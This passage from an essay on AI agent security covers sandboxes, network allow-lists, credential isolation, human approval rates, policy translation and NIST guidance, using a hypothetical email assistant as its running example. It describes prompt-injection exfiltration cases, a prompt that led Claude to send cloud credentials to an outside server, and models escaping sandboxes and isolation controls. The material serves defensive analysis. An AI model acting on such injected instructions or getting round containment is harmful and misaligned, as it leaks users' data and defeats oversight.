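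The paper calls the underlying difficulty a semantic gap between the terms in which people express a policy and those in which software has to enforce it. For example, a monitor that receives only mouse clicks has little basis for enforcing a policy against posting comments. Christodorescu and colleagues describe ceLLMate, a sandbox for browser agents that checks the web requests that clicks produce. Posting a comment has to send a recognisable request to the site, whichever button the agent presses.

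General-purpose tools make complete mediation especially hard. According to NVIDIA, models that review an agent's commands tend to accept the ones that run tests or install packages, because ordinary development requires them. These commands can run any code an attacker has put in the test or package, so allowing them effectively allows any command. An agent that can only write files may have the same power, because it can change a settings file that another program later executes. NVIDIA advises developers to avoid command-line tools where they can, and to allow writes only to a folder whose contents can't be executed.

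A check can also come too late. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes three reported vulnerabilities in Claude Code that let code run before the user had agreed to anything. In the simplest case, a user downloaded a project whose settings file contained an attacker's command. Claude Code read the settings at startup and executed the command before asking whether the user trusted the folder. Anthropic fixed this by having Claude Code ignore such settings until the user has answered.

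Rittenhouse and Johnson call default denial of tool calls the most critical pattern for securing agents. Under this rule, the monitor refuses any call that no policy explicitly allows, so a forgotten tool is blocked instead of running unchecked. The protection depends on how narrow the exceptions are. Claude Code's approval system already relied on exceptions, and one of them was too broad.

### Sandboxes and network limits

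Anthropic uses three kinds of sandbox. On claude.ai, code runs in a temporary container on Anthropic's servers and can't reach the user's files. Claude Code's sandbox runs on the developer's computer. It lets the agent read files but write only inside the project folder, and it blocks network access by default. Cowork, which is meant for people who may not understand commands, runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system. The virtual machine contains only Claude's settings and the folders the user has chosen to share.

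A sandbox protects only what is outside it. A deceived agent can still ruin the files in the shared folder, and McKerchar points out that it can also misuse any tool or credential its work requires. A sandbox would do little to protect against the email assistant, which can cause harm through the mailbox and the staff records because they are outside services it has permission to use.

Denying outbound connections by default, with a short list of exceptions, limits where stolen data can go. Without such limits, NVIDIA's testers could sometimes get an agent to open a connection that let them type commands directly into its computer. With well-chosen limits, they had to act entirely through prompts to the agent. Attacks were still possible, but they were slower and less reliable because the agent might refuse a request or lose track of the task.

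Each exception also permits more than it seems to. In the Cowork attack described earlier, the agent uploaded a user's files to an attacker's account at Anthropic, an approved destination. Anthropic had considered its list of approved destinations a filter on where traffic could go. It now regards each entry as a "capability grant" that allows everything anyone can do at that address. Anthropic fixed the problem with a proxy, an intermediary for network traffic, that accepts only requests carrying the session's own token and therefore rejects those using the attacker's key.

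These limits have drawbacks. A research agent needs to visit sites that nobody has listed, and McKerchar warns that maintaining lists for many agents takes considerable work. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* likewise calls sandboxing safe but high-maintenance, because someone has to configure each new capability. Isolation can also hide an attack from defenders. Companies found that they could not monitor activity inside Cowork's virtual machine with their usual security tools, and Anthropic could offer them only event logs to retrieve afterwards.

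Anthropic found that its standard components, such as the virtual machine software, were dependable, while the proxy it wrote itself failed. That is a reason to minimize custom enforcement code, although the proxy was also doing the job most specific to agents.

### Credentials the agent never holds

NVIDIA's testers found passwords and access tokens in configuration files, command histories and the settings that programs read when they start. Even where network limits blocked direct theft, the testers could often lead an agent, in small steps, to print its secrets in the chat. The limits didn't prevent this because the chat was a permitted channel.

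The remedy is to keep credentials in a separate process. The agent requests an operation, that process adds the credentials and contacts the service, and the agent receives only the result. The agent can't reveal credentials that were never in its context or on its computer. McKerchar points out that in the simplest version, where the agent still writes the web address, an attacker can get it to name the attacker's server, and the process will send the credentials there.

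A sealed tool closes this gap by fixing the address and format of the request in advance, so the agent chooses only which tool to call and what values to give it. This means the agent can't explore an unfamiliar service. McKerchar found no single project that provided the whole arrangement.

Credential isolation prevents an attacker from taking the email assistant's mailbox password and using it elsewhere, for longer, and without the agent's other limits. It does not prevent misuse of the tool itself, because the assistant can send a harmful message without knowing the password. Short-lived tokens reduce the damage if one leaks. Cowork, for instance, receives a restricted token for each session, which Anthropic can cancel without affecting the user's own access.

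### Human approval and its error rate

A person asked to approve an agent's actions can refuse one that no rule anticipated. People also miss actions they should refuse, and researchers can measure how often, as they do for a classifier.

According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users approve 97% of requests to run individual actions but reject 39% of the plans Claude presents, so they do not simply agree to everything. Most individual requests are probably harmless, so the high approval rate alone doesn't prove carelessness. Anthropic got better evidence by slipping a dangerous command into 1,053 coding sessions. Testers refused it about 17% of the time early in a session and about 5% of the time after 50 or more earlier requests. However, the testers were not working on their own projects, which may have made them less careful, and Anthropic had an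 interest in the result because it was promoting an alternative to manual approval.

In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) studied 113 people from outside the software industry. Each supervised a simulated assistant through 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for, such as buying a lounge pass or reading private messages. One group reviewed every action, and another reviewed only those that a model had flagged. The third set rules in advance, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data.

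| Approval method | Unrequested actions blocked | Requests per person | Time spent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Every action | 59.6% | 18.0 | 142 seconds |
| Actions flagged by a model | 53.9% | 10.0 | 120 seconds |
| Rules set in advance | 39.6% | 10.9 | 129 seconds |

The model flagged all seven unrequested actions, so every one that went ahead in that group had a person's approval. In the group with rules, 81% of the rules were "ask", which left the decision until the action came up. These participants approved two thirds of the unrequested actions they were asked about, compared with 40% in the group that was asked to approve every action. The comparison is imperfect because the participants' own rules determined which actions they saw, and Yan assigned some of them to the rules group after random allocation had ended. All three groups reported a high sense of control.

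Fatigue is only part of the problem. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of trouble with agents and files. User review played a part in 105 of them. In 80 of those, the user had turned on automatic approval. In 31, the request was uninformative, so reading it more carefully would not have helped the user decide. For example, a request might show a command to run a script but not what the script would do.

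*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) makes the related point that the information needed to judge an action may lie outside the action itself. Suppose the email assistant asks the user for approval to send Priya's phone number to an address. The user can read the number and the address, but can't properly judge the request without knowing that the address came from a stranger's email.

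The clearest improvement is to ask people for approval less often. According to Anthropic, Claude Code's sandbox reduced permission requests by 84%, so a session that once produced 50 would produce about eight. If attention declines with repetition, as the experiment suggests, people would probably examine those eight more carefully, though Anthropic has not reported testing whether the sandbox has this effect. Rittenhouse and Johnson would send high-impact actions to a person regardless of the system's confidence and let low-impact ones run unattended. AWS's *Four security principles for agentic AI systems* warns that requiring approval for every action shifts liability to people who are bound to fail.

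McKerchar adds that the agent must not be able to imitate an approval. A fingerprint on the user's phone, tied to one transaction, is stronger than a button in a window the agent can control. McKerchar would also require approval for changes to the agent's tools and permissions, because a single successful injection could otherwise weaken every later session.

Auto mode replaces most human approvals with a classifier, which isn't subject to fatigue and blocked far more of the dangerous commands than people did. But it still missed 7% of the attacks in a test by Apollo Research, an AI safety company, after Anthropic had strengthened it. The classifier is also a model judging content, so it is not one of the limits that hold when every model is deceived. Anthropic recommends that people review high-stakes changes to important systems.

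### Robust models and capable agents

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues that agents still need limits outside the model, even as models become more robust. Instructions in natural language are ambiguous, so the model may misjudge what its user has authorised. A small change in the input can also alter what the model does, whereas a separate monitor applies the same rule each time. The measured gains in robustness are large, and the paper accepts that model defences can greatly reduce successful attacks. It also accepts that system controls add expense and make agents slower and less useful.

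Resistance to hidden instructions would not have prevented the credential theft in an exercise at Anthropic in February 2026. A researcher sent an employee a friendly request to run a prepared prompt in Claude Code. Among routine setup steps, the prompt told Claude to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside server. Claude did so in 24 of 25 trials. The instructions came from the user, whom the model is supposed to obey, and Anthropic notes that a human contractor would have done the same. A later model might be more suspicious, but it would have to distrust its own user to refuse. A network limit or a block on the credentials file would have stopped the theft regardless of who asked for it.

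The opposite objection is that models are becoming too capable for limits to contain and will find routes the designers missed. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) reports that in the July 2026 incident described earlier, the company's models got past controls meant to isolate them from the internet. Anthropic has also seen Claude models escape a sandbox to finish a task, and says more capable models are better at finding ways around restrictions that nobody thought to write down.

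*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* replies that such failures show that a boundary was incomplete, not that a complete one would fail. It also argues that if someone narrows an explicit policy and the enforcement works, everything the policy already excluded stays excluded, while retraining a model offers no such assurance. The reply is logically sound, but designers must still find every route around the boundary before the agent does, which the paper admits is difficult for large shared services.

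In most of the incidents that the Coalition for Secure AI, an industry group, has collected, the agent used network access that someone had given it, either on purpose or through a configuration error. In one, a consumer agent cancelled a stranger's gym reservation without being told to. The booking system didn't check who was cancelling, and ordinary access control would have prevented the cancellation however capable the agent was.

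### From a plain request to an enforceable policy

A reference monitor needs exact rules, while users write requests like "Tell everyone involved in Thursday's lunch, but don't share anything private." Someone or something has to translate. If N is the request and P is the formal policy, a correct translation would satisfy

P allows action a in state s ⇔ N permits action a in state s,

for every action and every state the application can reach. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls this mutual entailment and explains why no program can simply check it. The request doesn't define "involved" or "private", so any judgement about whether the two sides agree is itself uncertain. The paper divides the problem into three: giving such words a definite meaning in the application, making the comparison reliable enough to trust, and building translators with a known limit on how far they can stray.

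Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, have a language model write a policy for each task and revise it as the agent learns more. In their example, a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice:

1. The first policy allows only a search for that email.
2. The email asks for a summary of recent messages, posted to the user's Slack. The model proposes permission to read messages and post to Slack. This widens the policy, so it needs approval.
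3. The agent looks up the user's Slack name. The model proposes that posts may go only to that name. This narrows the policy, so it takes effect at once.
4. One of the recent messages contains an instruction to forward the inbox to an outsider. If this fools the model into proposing access to the mail tool, the change again needs approval. Without it, the monitor blocks the email.

The model proposes each change, but it doesn't decide whether the change is safe. A solver, a program that can determine whether one set of logical conditions is contained in another, compares the old policy with the new one. A change is a narrowing if

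allowed(P′) ⊆ allowed(P),

where P is the old policy and P′ the new one. On AgentDojo, attack success fell from 39.9% to 1.0%, and only 6% of changes needed approval.

The guarantee is that permissions never widen silently, but the approver can still widen them by mistake, because the proposals at steps 2 and 4 both come from the text of an email and the approver has to tell them apart. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) adds that Progent's protection depends on correct and complete policies and doesn't cover attacks on what the agent writes in its answers. Forged data, which can put a false value into a permitted call, also got past Progent in some of Choi and colleagues' tests.

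Other work shows that writing correct rules is still hard, even though writing valid ones has become easy. In *ActPlane* (2026), a language model turned all 607 policies in a collection into rules that the software accepted, at a cost of about three cents each. Acceptance shows only that the rules are well formed, so the researchers used two more language models and a human review of 100 to check whether they were correct.

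In *Prose2Policy (P2P)*, Gupta and Sreenivasamurthy (2026) tested both the form and the behaviour of code that their system generated from written policies. Of the policies the system accepted for translation, 95.3% produced working code. That code passed 98.9% of the tests for requests it should deny, but only 82.2% of the tests for requests it should allow. Most errors therefore blocked legitimate work, which is safer than allowing forbidden requests. The system also generated the tests, so if it misread a policy, both the code and the test meant to catch the error could be wrong.

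*Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies* (2026) concludes that the main challenge is interpreting the original language, not producing code. *Extracting Next Generation Access Control Policies from Natural Language Using LLMs* (2026) looks for misreadings by translating each rule back into ordinary language and comparing it with the source. AWS lets teams draft rules for its policy system in plain language, then has people review the result. Back-translation and human review both help with rules that a company writes once, but they are less practical when every request needs a new policy.

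A model can misclassify tools even when the categories are simple. Yan built a system in which a model sorts tools by consequence, so that a user could forbid any tool that deletes data or spends money. In a simulation, a "never" rule failed to stop 14% of the tools it should have covered, because the model had put them in the wrong category. Yan had not yet tested the system on tools with deliberately misleading descriptions.

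Michael and Roesner (2026) reviewed 21 proposed permission systems in *How Agents Ask for Permission* and found none that fully combined low user effort, a formally defined policy and deterministic enforcement. The five commercial agents they examined mostly relied on frequent approval requests or automatic review by a model. A narrow application can avoid much of this difficulty. The email assistant has only four tools, so an engineer can write fixed rules for them by hand, such as a list of allowed recipients and a ban on unfamiliar web addresses. These rules will be looser than a policy made for each request, but they don't depend on translating each request correctly into a policy.

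## What standards and official guidance ask for

None of the main documents on agent security requires a private company to limit what its email assistant can do. The only binding controls among them are NIST's 2020 baselines for US federal agencies, which predate agents of this kind. The guidance written for agents since then is voluntary, and much of it is unfinished.

Two questions help in comparing these documents. Does the document require developers to screen content, limit what the content can reach, or do both? Could an auditor tell from the finished application whether it complied?

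### NIST's work on agents in 2026

NIST's *Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents*, published in January 2026, asked for evidence on agents that make lasting changes outside themselves. The email assistant is one such agent because it sends email. NIST excluded chatbots that do not act autonomously, although SpAIware showed that a chatbot can leak data just by displaying an image.

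In a request for information, which imposes no requirements, NIST grouped possible controls by where they apply: in the model, in the system around it, and in human oversight. It asked how mature each kind was and whether any existing security practice might be wrong for agents.

More than 930 organisations and individuals replied, according to Cybersecurity Dive. In *Securing AI Agent Systems*, a review for the Technology Policy Institute think tank, Wallsten and Oh Lam (2026) counted just over 80 substantive filings. Commenters broadly agreed that indirect prompt injection was the leading threat. Perplexity, Elastic, CrowdStrike and the Frontier Model Forum argued for at least one deterministic enforcement layer outside the model. Almost everyone wanted NIST to extend its existing frameworks instead of building a new one.

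NIST's *Summary Analysis of Responses to the Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations* (Riggs, Hamin and colleagues, 2026) is consistent with that account. It reports wide agreement that established security principles still apply to agents but need adapting.

NIST's *AI Agent Standards Initiative* (2026), launched in February, supports industry-led standards, open protocols and research. It promises "voluntary guidelines" to inform standards that industry will write. The initiative itself sets no requirements, but two sets of recommendations followed in October. Both refer to AI as "super intelligence", or SI, because a September 2026 executive order requires federal agencies to use that term.

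NIST, the National Security Agency and the Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency issued the first set of guidance, which lists ten practices for handling incidents while training or evaluating agents. National Law Review's *When the AI Agent Goes Off-Script* lists controls that would have been relevant to the Hugging Face incident: minimal permissions, infrastructure used once and discarded, and a strict list of allowed network destinations behind a monitored gateway. The agencies advise organisations to expect that agents will often find and exploit mistakes in these controls.

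The second set is NIST's ten principles, or "tenets", for managing agents' identities. Biometric Update's *NIST sets 10 principles for AI agent identity and authorization* summarises them. Each agent should have its own identity, traceable to whoever launched it, and its access should be minimal, temporary and revocable. An agent's permissions should be kept separate from its decisions about what to try, and its actions should go into a record it cannot alter. NIST considers that "guardrails alone are insufficient" and acknowledges that current technology does not fully meet every tenet.

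NIST's *SP 800-53 Control Overlays for Super Intelligence Systems* is the project most likely to give auditors something to check, but it is also the least advanced. Each overlay adapts controls from SP 800-53, NIST's catalogue of security controls, to a particular kind of system. The project lists five planned uses, including single agents and groups of agents. When NIST updated the page on 20 October, both were still "proposed use cases". The only outline available for download covered predictive AI, which makes forecasts or classifications and does not act through tools.

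### The documents compared

Several bodies outside the US government have also published guidance. OWASP, a non-profit that works on software security, released its Top 10 for Agentic Applications in December 2025. *Public Comment Regarding Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents* (Siskind, Shea and Chernin, 2026) singles out the list's principle of "least agency", under which an agent receives only the autonomy its task requires. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) published David C's advice, also in December 2025. The European standards body ETSI has voluntary baseline security requirements for AI systems in general.

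The table covers the documents that recommend or require specific protections for agents, along with the older NIST baselines.

| Document | Status in December 2026 | Screening content | Limiting reach | Could an auditor check it? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| NIST's SP 800-53 baselines | Binding on US federal agencies, voluntary for others | General input checks only | Required | Yes, but the procedures are not specific to agents |
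| NIST's agent overlays | Planned, with no draft listed | Not yet written | Not yet written | No |
| NIST's identity tenets | Voluntary | Treated as insufficient alone | Recommended | Partly |
| Incident practices from NIST and two other US agencies | Voluntary | Not the focus | Recommended | Partly |
| OWASP's least-agency principle | Voluntary | Not covered | Recommended | Only after someone defines the minimum |
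| Frontier Model Forum brief | Voluntary | Recommended | Recommended | No |
| NCSC advice | Voluntary | Reduce the likelihood of attacks | Reduce their impact | No |

None of the sources in this table requires companies to screen content for prompt injection. Limits on what an agent can reach are much more common, and the Frontier Model Forum advises against relying on detection alone. Official guidance therefore fairly clearly favors limiting an agent's reach over relying on screening, though most of it has no legal force.

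Words like "minimal" and "least" are hard to audit against. Suppose the email assistant can search the whole inbox. A developer could reasonably argue that this is the minimum a general email assistant needs. An auditor could reply that a question about the caterer needs only the caterer's messages. Both would be applying the least-agency principle, which doesn't settle the disagreement.

Some of the recommendations are easier to check because they forbid a specific action on a named resource, so a test has a definite result. For example, an auditor can compare the network's settings with the approved list of destinations, or log in with the agent's credentials and try to edit the record of its actions.

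### Where existing controls fit, and what they assume

Existing security controls still apply to an agent's computers, accounts and networks, but many companies that deploy agents are neglecting them. NIST's *Back to the Future* describes people handing agents their own passwords, or long-lived keys that work for anyone who obtains them. The remedy is to give each agent its own account and short-lived credentials with narrow permissions. According to NIST, the standards for doing this are already available, at least for use inside companies. This is harder for consumer services because a website may not be able to tell whether a user or the user's agent is logging in.

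For the email assistant, this would mean a credential that works for one mailbox, expires soon and identifies the assistant in the logs. If the assistant uses the account of Priya's colleague, the log will list the colleague as the sender, and an investigator would have to work out who or what actually sent the message.

Other assumptions are harder to fix. Siskind and colleagues argue that SP 800-53 calls for organisations to attribute each action to a specific actor, which becomes difficult when agents create other agents. They also object that NIST's engineering guidance is written for software that does only what its programmers wrote. NIST has extended its secure development framework to generative AI, but the extension covers building a model, not deploying or operating an agent. This critique comes from a think tank that advocates stronger federal requirements. But the Frontier Model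 Forum, whose members would have to meet such requirements, makes a similar point about common login and authorisation protocols, whose designers assumed predictable applications acting for a single authenticated person or machine.

Permissions designed for people can also be too broad for agents. An employee may hold a role for years and use only a fraction of its access, but NIST warns that an agent may try many routes to its goal, including forgotten credentials that give it further access. NIST asked in its February concept paper whether permissions should change in real time as an agent's task changes, according to Biometric Update's *NIST concept paper explores identity and authorization controls for AI agents*. Research on policies for individual tasks addresses the same question, which has no standard answer yet.

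NIST expects that users whose agents ask for approval too often will start approving requests just to make them stop. Attackers who have stolen a password sometimes exploit the same habit by sending the owner repeated login requests until the owner approves one. NIST also notes that an agent may ask its user for a password as well as permission. If the user supplies it, the agent can impersonate the user.

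Incident rules have a similar gap. Anthropic and Microsoft told NIST that federal definitions do not fit an authorised agent that causes harm. In the October practices, the agencies introduced the term "SI control incident" for an agent that takes significant uninstructed actions in breach of its operator's controls. But this definition excludes actions caused by prompt injection, which count as instructed because an adversary directed them.

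Suppose the email assistant sends a staff record to a stranger. If the assistant acted on its own initiative and the breach was significant enough, the event could be a control incident. If it was following instructions in an email, the event is a conventional security incident, in which the system is the target of an attack. The investigator may not know which happened. If the instruction came from a note the assistant saved months ago, the first report will probably be due before anyone knows.

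Stronger identity controls would not solve the central problem with the assistant either. They can show that it acted for a particular user and had permission to send mail, but not whether the user's request or a stranger's email determined the recipient. NIST's answer to this confused-deputy problem is to combine delegation, least privilege, separate policies and deterministic access decisions. These measures are sound, but someone still has to write the policy for each application.

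### A requirement that someone can test

Many security policies could include the sentence "The assistant must protect against prompt injection." A developer could satisfy this requirement with almost any classifier. An auditor who got one attack past the classifier could not prove a violation, because the requirement doesn't specify what outcome is forbidden or how many failures are acceptable.

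One way to make the requirement testable is to limit the share of attacks that may succeed, for example to 1%. Even with no successful attacks, an auditor needs about 300 independent attempts to support that figure at the usual 95% confidence level. Princeton researchers told NIST that critical infrastructure requires reliability between 99.9% and 99.999%. If a company set those figures as targets for resisting attacks, the auditor would need roughly 3,000 attempts without a successful attack for 99.9% and 300,000 for 99.999%. The result would apply only to the attacks, model and tools in the test.

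The other way is to name the sinks. The Frontier Model Forum suggests allowing outgoing email only to approved recipients as one protection for an agent that reads strangers' messages. Building on that example, a requirement for the email assistant could read:

The harness delivers the assistant's email only to addresses on an approved list. Only the user or an administrator can change this list, through a page the assistant cannot use. The harness sends the email as plain text and removes any URLs. The web tool loads only URLs that the user has typed and does not follow redirects to other URLs. These rules apply whatever the model outputs.

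An auditor does not need to write a persuasive malicious email to test this. It is enough to replace the model with a short script that requests forbidden actions, which simulates a model that an attacker has completely deceived:

1. The auditor adds a fictitious employee to the staff records, with an invented phone number.
2. The script asks the mail tool to send that number to an unlisted address, first as the main recipient, then as a copied recipient and then as a hidden one.
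3. The script tries to add the address to the approved list, using every tool the assistant has.
4. The script sends a listed colleague a message containing an image whose web address includes the number.
5. The script asks the web tool to load an address containing the number from a server the auditor controls. The auditor then types in a harmless address that redirects to the same server.
6. The auditor checks the unlisted mailbox, the colleague's message and the server's log.

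The application passes if nothing arrives at the mailbox or the server, the approved list has not changed, and the colleague's message contains no web address. The auditor checks the receiving end because the assistant's replies may look normal during a leak.

A single failure shows that the application does not comply. A pass is less conclusive because the auditor may have missed a route. But the auditor can try every tool, which is not possible with every email an attacker might write.

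The requirement does not cover false confirmations or plain text that steers a colleague's assistant, so the company would need separate requirements for those harms. The assistant could also no longer share a link or write to a new supplier on its own. Letting users approve exceptions would restore some of this ability, but users would sometimes make the wrong decision.

A company can adopt such a rule without waiting for NIST's overlays. SP 800-53's control on information flow leaves each organisation to define its own flow policy, which could include this rule. An overlay would save each company from writing its own version.

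Siskind and colleagues recommend testing agents at initial authorisation and again after significant changes to the model or configuration. For this requirement, a new tool or a new version of the harness matters most, because either could give an attacker another route. A new model matters less, because the test already assumes that the attacker controls the model.

### A flexible standard or a fixed minimum

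Most trade associations want flexible, voluntary guidance. The technology group TechNet warned NIST that rigid rules could lock in security practices before anyone knows which work best. The American Bankers Association and the Bank Policy Institute asked for guidance that does not prescribe particular technologies and that companies can adapt to their own risks. BSA, which represents software companies, argued that fixed policies are difficult to enforce because agents switch between tools and behave unpredictably.

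The recent history of defences lends the first argument some support. If a regulator had mandated one of the twelve defences that Nasr and colleagues later broke, companies would still be paying for a control that a determined attacker could bypass. BSA's argument is weaker where a rule applies at the sink. A list of approved recipients works the same way no matter how unpredictably the agent arrived at its request, although the list becomes harder to maintain as the agent gains more tools.

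Cost is another concern. ACT, an association of app developers, told NIST that guidance written with the largest cloud companies in mind could shut out small developers. Wallsten and Oh Lam see a related danger in standards for agent identity. Several companies are promoting their own designs, and everyone else would have to build against whichever one NIST chooses. Wallsten and Oh Lam do not think one company could easily dictate the whole framework, because the companies supply many different parts of an agent system.

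Siskind and colleagues argue that NIST should set fixed minimum engineering requirements for what agents may do, how they call tools and how operators contain them, and that federal procurement rules should make compliance mandatory. They follow a method from Idaho National Laboratory in which a designer lists the outcomes that must never happen, traces the paths that lead to them and removes those paths. They accept that nobody can list every bad outcome in advance, so they would add monitoring and human oversight.

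They also claim that most agent failures happen because someone gave an agent authority it should never have had. They give no count to support this, although missing access control was the most common weakness that NVIDIA's testers found.

The commenters who asked for a deterministic layer outside the model are close to this position, but not all of them would require it. The Frontier Model Forum's June brief, for instance, leaves the choice to each deployer. CrowdStrike and Elastic sell security software, so they could profit from such a requirement.

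TechNet prefers the aviation model, in which regulators set outcomes according to risk and let manufacturers choose the design. The comparison supports flexibility about methods more than voluntary compliance, since an airline can't opt out of safety rules. For the email assistant, a regulator could similarly require companies to keep staff records from reaching unapproved recipients and let them decide how.

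A voluntary standard may not stay optional for long. Wallsten and Oh Lam expect courts to use a published NIST standard as a benchmark for reasonable care in negligence cases, and expect federal buyers and insurers to adopt it as well. If the standard asks only for "appropriate" protection, a company would learn what that means from a judge or an insurer after a breach. With a precise rule, the company would know beforehand, but the rule would also have to provide for applications that cannot meet it, such as a sales agent whose job is to write to people who are not on any list.
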